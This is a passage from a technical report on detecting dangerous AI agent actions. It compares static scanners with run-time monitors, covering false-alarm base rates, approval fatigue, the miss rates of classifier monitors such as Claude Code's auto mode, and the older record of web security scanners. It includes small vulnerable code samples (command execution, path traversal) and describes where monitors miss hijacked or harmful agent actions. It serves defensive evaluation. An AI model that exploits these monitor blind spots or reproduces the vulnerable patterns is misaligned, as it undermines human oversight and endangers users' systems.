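A scanner that sees every path and a monitor that sees every call must still pick out the few that are dangerous. AgentSecGraph, the scanner presented in *Beyond Predefined Sinks*, searched 67 repositories of agent code for operations that could do harm, such as running a command, deleting a file or calling an outside service, and found 23,866. For 41.15% of these operations, it found evidence that text from the model or another outside source might reach them, and for 12.88% it found code that might act as a guard.

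These operations are candidates for review and shouldn't be counted as findings, because a coding agent has to run commands and write files to do its job. If a reviewer spent five minutes on each candidate, the list would take about 2,000 hours, or roughly a working year. Keeping only the candidates with evidence of data flow would cut this to about 800 hours, but it could also discard real problems. AgentSecGraph traced a flow into 84% of file writes but only 2% of browser actions, probably in part because the analysis follows data only over short distances.

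### Three tools that run the same command

The paper illustrates the difficulty with three tools that contain the same dangerous operation. In simplified form, they look like this:

```python
def tool_a(cmd):
    run(cmd)

def tool_b(cmd):
    cmd = "date"
    run(cmd)

def tool_c(cmd):
    if cmd in ALLOWED:
        run(cmd)
```

A scanner that only searches for `run` would report all three the same way. In `tool_a`, the model chooses the command, so an attacker who hijacks the model can choose it too. `tool_b` discards the model's text and always prints the date. `tool_c` is only as safe as its list of allowed commands. AgentSecGraph can distinguish the three, but it records only that `tool_c` has a check, so a person still has to judge whether the check is good enough.

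The researchers also reproduced 22 sensitive behaviours from 13 of the repositories under controlled conditions. One was a confirmed vulnerability, and another was still pending. The other 20 had guards or limits on their use and didn't qualify as vulnerabilities under the conditions tested.

AgentSecGraph's researchers found one vulnerability among the 22 behaviours they reproduced. They chose those behaviours rather than sampling at random, so the ratio can't be used to estimate how many of the tool's 23,866 candidates are vulnerabilities. AgentFlow's precision of 73%, by contrast, comes from checking a sample of its reports.

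### One attack in 10,000 sessions

This problem is harder for monitors, because harmful sessions may be much rarer than dangerous paths. Axelsson's *The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection* (2000) examines the problem in systems that search computer logs for break-ins. In its example, a small office's computers produce a million log records a day, 20 of them left by intruders. If a detector flags all 20, along with one in every 100,000 harmless records, about 66% of its alarms are real. If it flags all 20 and one in every 1,000 harmless records, only 2% of its alarms are real.

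The detection rate matters much less than the false-alarm rate. If the better detector caught only 70% of the intruders' records, the share of alarms that are real would fall from 66% to 58%. Axelsson concluded that the false-alarm rate is the limiting factor for such systems, since operators who receive mostly false alarms learn to ignore every alarm.

The same arithmetic applies to an agent's monitor. If *p* is the share of sessions that contain an attack, *r* is the monitor's recall and *f* is its false-positive rate, then:

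```text
harmless sessions blocked per attack stopped = f × (1 − p) / (r × p)
```

Take Tether's false-positive rate of 4.7%, and its perfect recall on the attacks it could follow:

| Share of sessions with an attack | Harmless sessions blocked per attack stopped | Share of blocks that stop an attack |
|---|---|---|
| 1 in 10,000 | 470 | 0.2% |
| 1 in 100 | 4.7 | 18% |
| 344 in 1,934, as in Tether's tests | 0.2 | 82% |

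The monitor is equally accurate in each row. Its blocks look well justified in the tests because more than one run in six contained an attack. If the retailer handled a thousand tickets a day and one in 10,000 were an attack, the monitor would stop one attack every ten days and block 47 harmless tickets a day. Its false-positive rate would have to be about 0.01% for it to block only one harmless ticket per attack.

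The figure of 470 is probably too pessimistic for Tether, since most of its refusals of harmless runs were correct under its policy. Counting only the 17 clearer errors gives about 107 blocked sessions per attack. Agents can also cause harm without an attacker. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes agents that deleted remote branches of code after misreading an instruction, or tried to alter a production database. More sessions therefore contain something worth stopping than contain an attack, though the retailer is unlikely to know either share in advance.

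Small tests are little help at these rates. *Parallax* (2026) reports that a monitor in its default configuration blocked none of 50 legitimate actions, but its true false-positive rate could still be up to about 6%. If one action in 10,000 were harmful, that rate would mean about 600 legitimate actions blocked for each harmful one stopped.

### What a false alarm costs

A false finding takes up a developer's time once, but a false block can interrupt work every time the same situation comes up. Suppose the scanner in the earlier example produces 12 false findings and a programmer needs 20 minutes to dismiss each. That takes four hours, and the programmer can record the decisions so that the next scan doesn't report the same findings unless the code changes. If the monitor blocks 47 harmless tickets a day and a worker spends five minutes on each, that takes almost four hours every day for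 as long as the agent runs. The 20 minutes and five minutes are invented figures.

Blocks are less disruptive when no person has to deal with them. In Claude Code's auto mode, a language model reviews actions in place of the user. When it blocks an action, the agent receives the reason and tries something safer. According to Anthropic, a false positive then leads to a single retry. After three blocks in a row, or 20 in a session, a person has to take over. If nobody is available, the run ends.

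A dangerous path that the scanner misses stays in the code until somebody finds it, and any later ticket can trigger it. When the run-time monitor misses a harmful action, only that action gets through, although an attacker who finds the gap can use it again.

### How carefully people approve

A monitor that is unsure about a call can ask a person instead of refusing it. This replaces a false block with a prompt, which is an improvement only if the person reads it. Anthropic's engineering post on auto mode says that users accept 93% of Claude Code's permission prompts. A later post, Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), gives 97%. These rates don't prove that users are careless, because most of the commands were probably safe. The later post also reports that users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents for approval, but they may simply prefer another approach,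 so comparing plans with permission prompts gives only weak evidence about security.

In an experiment described in the same post, a research vendor had 1,053 paid testers work on coding tasks and replaced one permission prompt in each session with a request to run a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it, while auto mode refused 89% of the same commands. Testers caught about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

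One would expect this drop from approval fatigue, in which people stop reading requests because there are so many. But fatigue can't be the whole explanation, since testers missed about 83% of the dangerous commands even early on. They were working in a test environment rather than on their own code, so they had less to lose by approving. Anthropic also makes the product that performed better.

Data from real use support the same conclusion. Among sessions that Anthropic's safety systems had flagged, 6.3% of those with manual approval contained serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly asked for, compared with 2.4% of those in auto mode. A model graded the harm. Users chose their own mode, so differences in their work may explain some of the gap. The percentages cover only flagged sessions, so they aren't base rates for all sessions.

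In *Let the Agent Do It?*, Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026) surveyed 107 software practitioners about permissions. 47.7% said they read requests carefully, 20.6% said they approved them by default, and 33.6% said they had become less careful over time. People tend to overstate their diligence, so they may be less careful than these figures suggest.

Reviewing an agent's code carefully doesn't seem to make developers much more careful about approving its actions. *From Delegation to Action Approval* (Wu, Wermke and colleagues, 2026) surveyed 203 developers and found that 64% often approved at least one type of agent action without close review. This included 61% of those who carefully reviewed most or all of the agent's code and 67% of the rest, a difference that could be due to chance. Developers who knew of security or privacy problems with agents were more likely to approve actions without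 close review (70%) than those who didn't (43%). This gap remained after the researchers adjusted for how often and how long people had used agents, since heavy users might both hear of more problems and approve more actions.

Approval prompts are often hard to judge. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analysed 290 reports of trouble with agents and files, and found that user review had contributed to 105 of them. In 80, the user had let the agent act without asking. In 31, the prompt showed a command but not its effect on the files. Wu, Wermke and colleagues found that developers who inspected diffs, which show what has changed in a file, were less likely to approve destructive commands or access to secrets.

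False alarms can cause misses if they lead users to turn a monitor off, because its published recall applies only while it is running. Anthropic reports that a quarter of interactive Claude Code sessions start with permission prompts switched off.

### Whether fewer prompts help

One remedy is to ask users for approval less often. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) reviews how products do this and finds that they either let the agent do more without asking, as an "always allow" button does, or rely on someone to have configured a sandbox correctly.

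Fewer prompts also don't guarantee more careful answers. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, Yan (2026) had 113 people without software backgrounds supervise a simulated assistant through 18 actions. Seven of these, such as reading private messages or buying a lounge pass, went beyond what the user had asked for. One group approved or denied every action and blocked 59.6% of the unrequested ones. Another group first set a standing rule of "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four categories, including spending and deleting. The second group received about 11 prompts instead of 18, but its block rate for unrequested actions was about 20 percentage points lower.

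Participants set 114 of the 140 standing rules to "ask", so the rules decided very little in advance. When the assistant asked about an unrequested action, participants with rules approved it 67% of the time, compared with 40% in the group without rules. Perhaps people who had already set rules assumed that whatever still reached them was acceptable. The two rates aren't strictly comparable, because people with rules received prompts only for the categories they had left open. Some of the actions were mild, such as phoning the airport to confirm a flight, so approving them wasn't always a mistake.

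If a worker at the retailer had to approve every reply, they would get a thousand prompts a day and would probably start approving them without checking. If the agent asked only when the recipient's address differed from the one on the ticket, the worker might get a handful of prompts a day, and it would be obvious what to check in each.

### Which method can catch which hazard

A single error rate also doesn't show which hazards a method misses. Even an otherwise accurate scanner or monitor can't detect some hazards.

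| Hazard | Scanner before deployment | Monitor at run time |
|---|---|---|
| Exposed credential | Yes, because the password is in a file | No, if a thief logs in without using the agent |
| `eval` without a sandbox | Yes, if it can trace the model's text to the call | In part: it can check the text, or limit the program's effects from the operating system |
| Over-broad file access | Yes, because the permission is in the settings | Yes, if each file operation passes through it |
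| Poisoned tool description | Yes, if the description exists at scan time and contains recognisable instructions | In part: it can check a new description on arrival, or refuse the calls that result |
| Permitted email to the wrong person | In part: it can report that the model chooses the recipient | Yes, if it has a trusted record of the right recipient |
| Leak across several permitted calls | In part: it can report that a route exists | Yes, if it remembers earlier calls or labels the data |
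| Harmful edit to a permitted file | No, because the edit doesn't exist yet | Only if a model or a person judges the content |

Scanners are good at finding problems with credentials, `eval` calls and file permissions because these are in the code or settings before the agent runs. Agent Audit, for instance, found 40 of 42 marked flaws, most of which were of these kinds. A monitor can still reduce the damage from an `eval` call that the scanner missed.

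A poisoned tool description is harder to catch if it is false but contains no suspicious instructions, because a scanner then has to compare it with the tool's code. Some monitors rely on descriptions too. Yan built one that sorts tools into categories by their names and descriptions, but tested it only on ordinary descriptions, so it might do worse on misleading ones. Yan warns that it isn't reliable enough to be the only safeguard.

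A monitor that checks only where an address came from can miss an email to the wrong person. AgentCap, the monitor by Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao, checks the address's source, so it would refuse one planted in a ticket. But if two customers are called J. Reed and the model takes the wrong one's address from the verified customer database, the address would pass this check because its source is trusted. The retailer's own rule would catch the mistake because it compares the recipient with the customer on the ticket.

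Almost every support agent can both read customer records and send email, so a scanner that warns about leaks across several permitted calls would flag almost all of them. These warnings are most useful for deciding where a run-time monitor needs a rule that considers earlier calls, or labels that track data.

Harmful edits to permitted files are the biggest gap. Auto mode lets an agent edit files inside the project without review by the classifier, the model that judges actions, because developers can inspect and undo such changes later. *Measuring the Permission Gate*, an independent test of auto mode, found that these edits made up 36.8% of the actions that changed something. *Shall We Approve?* (Wu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) presents Caper, a monitor that also leaves file edits to the agent's existing checks. Caper might stop harmful code when a later command runs it, but it doesn't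 check an edit that does damage by itself, such as overwriting a settings file. Reviewing the diff is the natural safeguard, and a company can also scan the edited code again before releasing it.

### Moving the threshold

Most checks can be made stricter, which usually catches more harmful cases but also stops more harmless ones. Auto mode is an unusually clear example because Anthropic published its error rates at two levels of caution. A fast first stage errs towards refusal, and a second stage reconsiders whatever the first flagged, using more careful reasoning.

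| | Harmless calls refused | Real unauthorised actions allowed | Artificial data leaks allowed |
|---|---|---|---|
| First stage alone | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
| Both stages | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

The second stage removes about 95% of the false refusals but raises the share of real unauthorised actions missed from 6.6% to 17%. If one call in 1,000 is harmful, then over 10,000 calls the first stage alone would catch about one more harmful call than the full system and refuse about 800 more harmless ones. Anthropic judged the extra refusals unacceptable for a coding assistant, but a bank using an agent to move money might decide differently.

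The 17% miss rate is uncertain because it comes from only 52 actions, about nine of which the classifier missed. The true rate could plausibly be anywhere from 9% to 30%. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier had detected the danger but wrongly treated it as something the user had agreed to. Anthropic doesn't recommend auto mode as a replacement for careful human review of high-stakes infrastructure.

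If each harmless call has a 0.4% chance of being wrongly refused and the errors are independent, about a third of sessions with 100 harmless calls will have at least one wrong refusal. At Gusto, a payroll company that uses auto mode, about 10% of sessions include a refusal of some kind.

A scanner such as Agent Audit suppresses findings that score below a threshold. The repaired `query_orders` and a dangerous version that only checks that `sql` is a string both score 0.18. The default threshold of 0.30 hides both, and lowering it to 0.15 would report both. No threshold can separate them, so the scanner would need a rule that distinguishes the two checks.

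A monitor that applies fixed rules has no score, but narrower rules have the same effect as a stricter threshold. If `send_email` may write only to the ticket's customer, the monitor will block the email when a customer asks the agent to copy in a spouse. If the tool may write to any customer, the monitor may still block the spouse, and a hijacked agent can send one customer's details to another. AgentCap's rules reduced task completion by between 3 and 12 percentage points, but far fewer attacks succeeded.

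Sending doubtful cases to a person also reduces misses but adds false alarms. Yan simulated a "never" rule with the monitor that categorises tools. The monitor failed to stop 14% of the tools the rule should have covered and wrongly stopped 4% of the others. When it asked the user about tools it was unsure of, only 11% of the forbidden tools could run without review, but it needlessly stopped or asked about 7% of the others. The extra questions help only if people answer them well. Because people pay less attention as prompts accumulate, asking about more calls could eventually increase both kinds of error.

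### Better evidence instead of a stricter setting

Some improvements reduce both errors. Wu, Chen and colleagues tested Caper on 102 tasks in which a harmless-looking command runs a tool that secretly deletes or overwrites a file. Each task had a safe twin with the same request and the same command, but with harmless code in the tool. They varied the information that the approving model received:

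| What the approver receives | Dangerous tasks that end in harm | Safe twins blocked |
|---|---|---|
| The command | 44.1% | 52.0% |
| The whole conversation | 17.6% | 61.8% |
| The conversation and a model's prediction of the effects | 3.9% | 61.8% |
| The conversation and the observed effects | 7.8% | 1.0% |

Giving the approver the whole conversation made it more suspicious, but it still couldn't tell the twins apart because the conversation doesn't show what the tool does. Giving it predicted effects reduced harm but not false blocks. Caper gets the observed effects by running the command in a sandbox before committing the result, much as Tether does, and gives the approver a short report of them. The median approval took 3.2 seconds. The tests didn't include an attacker who had adapted to Caper, for example with a tool that behaves well the first time it runs, so the 7.8% could be higher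 against such an attacker.

In the independent test of auto mode, by contrast, both errors got worse. *Measuring the Permission Gate* used 128 requests that deliberately left the target or the scope of the work unclear. The classifier missed 70.3% of the harmful actions it received and refused 31.9% of the harmless ones. Including file edits that it never received raised the miss rate to 81.0%. A stricter setting would reduce those misses only by refusing even more harmless work. Asking the user which target they meant would supply the missing information.

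Anthropic has since given the classifier more context, such as whether a code repository is public. Apollo Research, an AI safety company, tested it on artificial attacks before and after the changes, and the miss rate fell from 12% to 7%. On attacks that Anthropic never had access to, the new version caught about half of those the old version had missed, but missed about 2% of those the old version had caught.

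A classifier can cause false alarms when it judges a kind of input it wasn't trained on. At its strictest setting, the monitor in *Parallax* blocked 18 of 50 legitimate actions, including some emails. One classifier caused 14 of these blocks because it was trained to recognise the text of prompt injections but was judging tool calls, which look quite different.

Once a company has the best evidence it can get, the right threshold depends on the cost of each error. Refusing a call makes sense when:

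```text
P(harmful) × cost of harm  >  P(harmless) × cost of refusal
```

Suppose a wrong refusal costs the retailer £2 of a worker's time. If leaking the customer list would cost £200,000, the monitor should refuse an email that has even a 1 in 100,000 chance of containing it. For a £40 refund, it should refuse only if the chance that the claim is false exceeds about 1 in 21. A single threshold for all tools would therefore be too lax for email, too strict for refunds, or both. A monitor that only compares addresses doesn't estimate probabilities, but the retailer can apply the same reasoning by writing strict rules for `send_email` and looser ones for small refunds.

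## What the record of application security testing shows about coverage

Companies have used tools to scan and monitor ordinary web applications for over twenty years. Researchers have tested these tools on flaws that other people had already found in real programs, which measures coverage more fairly than a test designed by a tool's own makers, like the one used for Agent Audit.

### Five ways to check a web application

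Suppose the retailer also has an ordinary website, where customers type in an order number and the site looks it up in a database, and the order form is open to SQL injection. Security engineers have five standard ways to find or block this flaw:

| Method | What it observes | Nearest equivalent for agents |
|---|---|---|
| Static application security testing (SAST) | The code, without running it | Agent Audit and AgentFlow |
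| Dynamic application security testing (DAST) | A running application's replies to test requests | AgentFuzz's test prompts |
| Interactive application security testing (IAST) | Data moving inside the application during tests | Data labels like those of FIDES, used in testing |
| Runtime application self-protection (RASP) | Data moving inside the application in live use | AEGIS's hook in the agent's process |
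| Web application firewall | Requests and replies on the network | A proxy in front of the tool servers |

A static tool traces user input through the code from the web form to the database query. A dynamic tool submits odd characters through the form and checks the reply for a database error. An interactive tool adds sensors to the program and can record that the test input reached the database call, even if the reply looks normal. Self-protection uses similar sensors on live traffic and can stop the query. A firewall receives only the request and estimates from its text whether it is an attack.

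### How many known flaws static tools find

Habib and Pradel (2018), in *How Many of All Bugs Do We Find?*, ran three widely used static tools on 15 Java projects with 594 known bugs. According to Liu, Chen and colleagues (2023), the tools missed 95.5% of them, which means they found about 27. The 594 bugs were of all kinds, not only security flaws, and some were mistakes in a program's own logic that match no general pattern.

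Tests on security flaws alone gave better results, but the scores depend heavily on what counts as finding a flaw. Lipp, Banescu and Pretschner (2022), in *An Empirical Study on the Effectiveness of Static C Code Analyzers*, ran six tools on 27 programs with 192 known vulnerabilities and counted the misses in four ways:

| What counts as finding a flaw | Missed by the best tool | Missed by the best combination |
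|---|---|---|
| Flagging any affected function, for any reason | 47% | 30% |
| Flagging any affected function, with the right class of flaw | 70% | 57% |
| Flagging every affected function, for any reason | 64% | 43% |
| Flagging every affected function, with the right class of flaw | 80% | 69% |

Combining tools helped because they found different flaws, but it also created much more work. Under the loosest rule, the best combination found 34 more vulnerabilities than the best single tool and flagged an additional 15% or so of the 55,203 functions, which is roughly 240 extra functions to review for each extra vulnerability. CodeQL might have scored better, but it produced no results for a group of programs with 59 of the flaws, even after running for two weeks, and Lipp and colleagues counted all 59 as misses.

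Li, Chen and colleagues (2023), in *Comparison and Evaluation on Static Application Security Testing (SAST) Tools for Java*, tested seven free tools on 165 programs, each with one known vulnerability. The best tool, Horusec, found 21 of the vulnerabilities, and all seven tools together found 48, or 29%. Here too, the results depended heavily on what counted as a detection. Semgrep flagged a vulnerable file in 60 of the programs, but it identified both the right function and the right weakness in only nine.

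The researchers also scanned a repaired version of each program. The seven tools made 72 correct detections, but in 41 of these cases the tool still reported the flaw after the repair. SpotBugs, with a security plug-in, did so for 16 of its 17 correct detections. These tools had probably reacted to a suspicious pattern that remained after the repair. A programmer who fixes such a flaw cannot tell from the scanner whether the fix worked.

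### Why synthetic tests gave higher scores

Li and colleagues ran the same seven tools on the OWASP Benchmark, a set of 2,740 small test cases written for testing scanners. About half contain a flaw, and the rest are harmless lookalikes. They scored the tools by F1, which combines precision *P* and recall *R* as 2*PR*/(*P* + *R*):

| Tool | F1 on the synthetic cases | Real flaws found, of 165 |
|---|---|---|
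| Contrast | 84.4% | 1 |
| SpotBugs with plug-in | 82.8% | 17 |
| Semgrep | 79.8% | 9 |
| CodeQL | 49.0% | 11 |
| Horusec | 29.7% | 21 |
| SonarQube | 27.0% | 9 |
| Insider | 13.9% | 4 |

The tool that performed best on the synthetic cases performed worst on real programs, so the synthetic scores were a poor basis for choosing a tool.

Synthetic cases are easier mainly because the dangerous data takes a short, direct route. The following code adapts two of the researchers' Java examples. In both, a visitor can open files that the site never meant to share:

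```python
# Typical synthetic case
def show_photo(request):
    name = request.cookie("photo")
    return open(PHOTO_DIR + name)

# Typical real case
class Photo:
    def __init__(self, path):
        self.path = tidy(path)

    def load(self):
        return open(self.path)
```

In `show_photo`, the visitor's text reaches `open` within one function. In `Photo`, one function stores the text in `self.path` and another uses it later, so a scanner has to connect the two. It also has to detect that `tidy` doesn't remove every dangerous path. A CodeQL rule that the researchers examined treats a value as safe after any check at all, and Agent Audit has a similar weakness. Agent Audit also follows data only within one function, so it would have trouble with `Photo`.

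Synthetic tests of tools that analyze C code have the same weakness. According to Lipp and colleagues, each flaw in these tests is usually a change to a single instruction, and in many of the tests the tools find around 80% of the flaws.

Better rules could have caught most of the 117 flaws that all seven tools missed in the Java study, and mathematical limits on static analysis explain few of the misses. For 90 of the flaws, at least one tool had a relevant rule, but it was too simple to catch the flaw. Another 24 were of kinds that static analysis handles badly, such as requests that make a program use up its memory. No tool had a rule for the remaining three.

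More sophisticated analysis didn't always find more flaws. Horusec, which mostly searches for text patterns, found more than the tools that trace data. It also includes a program that compares an application's libraries with published lists of vulnerable versions, and this found another 49 of the 165 flaws. A company could check its MCP servers in the same way, but this would find only flaws that are already published.

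### Testing from outside

A dynamic tool can detect flaws only in the parts of a site it reaches. It first crawls the site, following links and listing the forms it finds. It then sends hostile input to each form and checks the replies for signs that an attack worked.

Doupé, Cova and Vigna (2010), in *Why Johnny Can't Pentest*, tested 11 black-box web vulnerability scanners on a photo-sharing site they had built with 16 flaws. Every scanner missed the same eight. A group of students with average security skills found 15 of the 16.

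Some of the missed flaws were on pages that the tools couldn't reach. Reaching one required logging in, commenting on a photo and confirming a preview. Another required uploading a picture, which none of the tools managed to do. The tools also missed a coupon that customers could apply repeatedly until their order was free. The site worked normally, so a tool could detect the flaw only if it had a rule that each coupon should work once. The retailer has a similar problem with refunds, since a refund for a vase falsely reported as broken looks like any other.

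False alarms varied even more than misses. One tool produced none, and another produced between 215 and 317, depending on its settings. These tools are old and the researchers tested them on only one site, so the figures are weak evidence about current products. But the results of any outside test depend on how much of the application it reaches.

Testing an agent from outside is harder because a model can respond differently to the same text. If an attack works 1% of the time, a tester who tries it 100 times has a 37% chance of never succeeding, while a criminal who files thousands of tickets would probably succeed.

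### Whether developers fix what scanners find

A finding makes an application safer only if somebody acts on it. *Lessons from Building Static Analysis Tools at Google* describes how the company began running FindBugs, a static tool for Java, every night in 2006 and listed the results on a dashboard. FindBugs found hundreds of bugs, but few engineers used the dashboard. In 2009, hundreds of engineers spent a week on the warnings. They reviewed 3,954 and filed bug reports for 44% of them, but fixed only 16%. Many of the bugs were real but not important enough to fix.

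Google later showed programmers findings while they were still working on the code. It turned its most reliable checks into compiler errors, which a programmer has to fix before the program will build. Less certain findings appear as comments when a colleague reviews the change. In a survey, engineers considered 74% of the problems flagged by the compiler to be real, compared with 21% of those found in code that Google had already accepted. The gap is partly because testing and review had removed many serious mistakes from the accepted code.

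In *Scaling Static Analyses at Facebook*, Distefano, Fähndrich and colleagues recommend reporting a problem when an engineer submits a change. In one case, engineers fixed about 70% of the problems reported this way, but none of those on a separate list outside their normal work.

False alarms can lead developers to ignore a tool altogether. *A Few Billion Lines of Code Later*, by the makers of the commercial scanner Coverity, puts the threshold at about 30% false positives, above which users stop paying attention and real bugs get lost among the false ones. They aim for less than 20%. Reviewers judged 27% of AgentFlow's sampled reports wrong.

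Google sets a limit of 10% for "effective false positives" among comments in code review. This broader definition covers any finding the developer doesn't act on, even if the tool was right. About once a week, a programmer complained that one Google check was mistaken. The check was correct each time, and the complaints stopped when the team reworded its message. Coverity responded to similar confusion by dropping some checks. For many years it didn't report errors in how parallel parts of a program interact, because many users couldn't follow the explanations.

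False positives also accumulate over repeated scans. Chou (2005) points out in *False positives over time* that developers fix real defects but tend to leave falsely flagged code unchanged. Suppose a scanner reports 100 problems, 80 of them real, and developers fix those 80. The next scan reports the 20 false ones again, along with ten new findings, eight of which are real. Only eight of the 30 findings are now real, although the scanner is as accurate as before. Coverity reduces this problem by recording which findings users have marked as false.

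Users don't always welcome a more thorough scanner. One company had fixed about 1,200 of the 2,400 errors that Coverity had reported. It then upgraded to a new version, which reported 3,600. The manager was furious that the team's progress seemed to have vanished and that the old version had missed so much. Some companies avoid upgrading for this reason.

These pressures favour simple checks that programmers can understand at once. Google didn't run analyses that trace data between functions across its whole codebase, so it would probably have missed flaws like the one in `Photo`. Facebook, however, used deeper analysis on codebases of up to 100 million lines and still got engineers to fix what it found.

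### Code that scanners skip on purpose

Coverity's makers also deliberately let their tool miss some bugs. It skipped code that caused too many false alarms or was too complicated to analyse, sometimes ignoring whole files. They describe this approach as almost standard among commercial products.

In *In Defense of Soundiness* (2015), Livshits and colleagues call an analysis "soundy" if it accounts for everything a program might do, except for a few language features that the tool's designers knowingly leave out. Common omissions are `eval` and reflection, which lets a program look up a function by name while it runs. They ask toolmakers to state which features they omit, so that users don't mistake a clean result for a guarantee.

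An agent's software may use reflection to run a tool:

```python
tool = getattr(tools, call.name)
result = tool(**call.arguments)
```

A sound scanner would have to assume that the first line could select any function in `tools`. In a large program that uses reflection heavily, these assumptions connect so many functions that the results become useless. Skipping reflection may be a reasonable compromise for a program that seldom uses it, but for an agent it could mean skipping every tool call. AgentFlow avoids the problem by reading the agent's declared list of tools, which narrows the possibilities to a handful of functions.

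### Firewalls and permission prompts

A web firewall is useful when nobody can change the application behind it, but attackers can reword their requests to get past it. Demetrio and colleagues showed in 2020 that software could automatically rewrite SQL injections to get them past firewalls that used machine learning. Rewritten prompt injections got past PIGuard in much the same way, but rewriting gave attackers no advantage against Progent, whose decisions don't depend on the attacker's wording.

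Android, Google's phone operating system, has asked users for permissions both in advance and during use. At first, each app listed the permissions it wanted at installation, and the user had to accept them all or cancel. Felt and colleagues (2012) found that only 17% of participants paid attention to the list during installation. In a separate survey, only 3% of respondents correctly answered all three questions about what permissions meant.

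Since Android 6.0, released in 2015, apps have had to ask for sensitive permissions, such as access to the user's location, while they are running. The user can refuse a permission and keep the app. Asking at run time gives the request some context. For example, a map app may ask for the user's location when they try to find a route.

One answer to a permission prompt may still cover many later uses that the user wouldn't have approved. Wijesekera and colleagues (2015) recorded how apps used their permissions on 36 people's phones and then interviewed the owners. At least 80% of the owners wanted to block at least one request, and overall the owners wanted to block more than a third of requests. The phones used the older permission system, but an "always allow" button in an agent can also permit actions the user would have blocked.

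Static analysis was useful for a different part of the problem, detecting excess permissions. In 2011, Felt and colleagues compared the permissions requested by 940 Android apps with the functions the apps called and found that about a third requested more than they needed. A scanner can do this well because the requests and the function calls are both in the app. The retailer could use a similar check to find out whether its mail tool's password also gives access to the inbox.

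### Two answers to SQL injection

AMNESIA, which Halfond and Orso presented in 2005, combines a scanner and a monitor. Before release, it finds each place where a Java web application sends a query to its database. It then analyses the code to work out what form each query can legitimately take. For the retailer's order page, the result might be:

```text
SELECT status FROM orders WHERE order_id = [value]
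```

AMNESIA also adds a check just before each database call. If a user types 5531, the query matches the expected form and the check lets it through. If the input adds another condition, the query contains extra SQL after the value and no longer matches, so AMNESIA blocks it. Nobody has to write a policy or list known attacks, because AMNESIA derives the rule from the application's code.

Halfond and Orso tested AMNESIA on seven web applications with large numbers of legitimate and malicious inputs. It stopped every attack and blocked no legitimate query. But it checks only the form of a query, so a visitor who typed another customer's order number would get that customer's order. And if the static analysis can't determine how the program builds a query, the expected form may be too loose and let attacks through.

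Parameterised queries solve the same problem much more simply. The database never treats the value as SQL, so there is no need to infer the right form or check it at run time. A scanner can still look for queries built by joining pieces of text, which is much easier than determining whether hostile input can reach them. Parameters can't replace some parts of a query, such as table names, so programmers may also need a list of allowed names.

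AMNESIA's method of deriving rules from code doesn't work for an agent, because the code lets the agent call any of its tools in any order. Narrow tools, such as a `send_email` that looks up the address itself, come closer to parameterised queries. That design protects the choice of recipient but not the message, which the model still writes after reading a stranger's text.

### Scanners built on language models

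Most of the miss rates above come from tools that apply fixed rules. *Towards LLM-Enhanced Android Taint Analysis* (Miazzo, Alecci and colleagues, 2026) instead uses a language model agent to look for private data leaking from Android apps. The agent uses MCP tools to search an app's code and follow data from one function to another. The researchers ran it several times on each app and kept only the leaks it reported in most runs.

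They compared two models with FlowDroid, a widely used static tool, on a public test set called DroidBench:

| | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|
| FlowDroid | 83% | 42% |
| Gemini 3 Flash | 96% | 95% |
| Qwen3.5-27B | 87% | 89% |

The models did especially well on some features that ordinary scanners tend to skip. Both had perfect scores on reflection, where FlowDroid's F1 score was 50%, and on code written in a lower-level language, where FlowDroid scored zero. But both models scored zero on apps that load more code while running, where FlowDroid scored 50%. Agents that install new tools could present a similar difficulty.

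These results may be too optimistic because DroidBench consists of 190 synthetic cases. It has also been public for years, so the models may have been trained on it. FlowDroid ran with its default settings, although other researchers have built extensions for some of the cases it missed.

The researchers also tested Gemini on five real apps, where it reported 17 data flows that FlowDroid had missed. Two reviewers confirmed 16 of them, which is a good result because tools that report more usually produce more false alarms. Gemini missed several flows that FlowDroid reported, so using both would find more than using either alone. Five apps are too few to estimate a general error rate.

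If models do this well on larger sets of real programs, the older miss rates could become obsolete. Weak rules explained most of the flaws that all seven Java tools missed, and a model doesn't need a hand-written rule for each pattern. Running current models on the 165 Java programs and their repaired versions would be a good test, but many of those flaws have been public for years, so the test would also need flaws too recent to be in the models' training data.

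A model can also give different results each time it scans the same code. The majority rule in the Android study discarded some real leaks because they appeared in only a minority of runs. Coverity's customers wanted the same results from one scan to the next, and its makers tried to keep changes in results below 5% even when they released a new version.

A scanner built on a language model may also be open to prompt injection. An attacker could put text in a malicious MCP server's code that leads the model to classify the server as safe. Combining the model with ordinary program analysis could limit the damage, provided the model can't dismiss a finding by itself. Miazzo and colleagues suggest a combination so that ordinary tools can handle the simple cases with few resources, leaving the difficult ones to the model.

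### Applying the record to agents

The older miss rates don't apply directly to agents. Many of the C flaws were memory errors, which are rare in agent code written in Python. Most known flaws in MCP servers are taint-style, and static tools may do better on these. In the Java study, at least one tool found each of the four most severe injection flaws. Four cases are too few for a prediction, but they suggest a scanner might miss fewer flaws in an MCP server than in a typical C program.

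The design of the older studies is easier to reuse. Researchers could run every agent scanner on the MCP server flaws that Shi, Fu and colleagues collected, then on the repaired versions, and count a flaw as detected only if the scanner reports it before the repair and not after. This test would show whether Agent Audit's 95% recall holds on flaws that its makers didn't choose.

Warnings about an agent's tools should also be more useful when programmers see them while writing the code. A programmer who has just added `send_email` to an agent's list of tools can easily reconsider the choice or add an approval step. Six months later, the same warning on a dashboard might go to someone who doesn't know why the agent needs email. A scanner could group its findings by tool, so that a programmer with 18 risky paths to the same email tool has only one decision to make.

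Much of the older evidence is about people's patience with false alarms, which may matter less as coding agents take over repairs. A coding agent could investigate 300 false alarms without losing trust in the scanner. It could also "fix" harmless code and introduce new bugs, so someone would still have to test its changes. In 2018, programmers at Google were already applying about 3,000 automatic repairs a day, but a person approved each one.

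Fix rates will also be harder to interpret. On the retailer's website, a path from the order form into the text of a query is a mistake that the programmer can remove. The support agent, however, needs a path from a ticket to an email to answer customers. If the programmer adds a rule to the runtime monitor instead of changing the code, Google's definition should count that as acting on the finding, but a scanner that looked only for changes in the code would report the same path again the next day.
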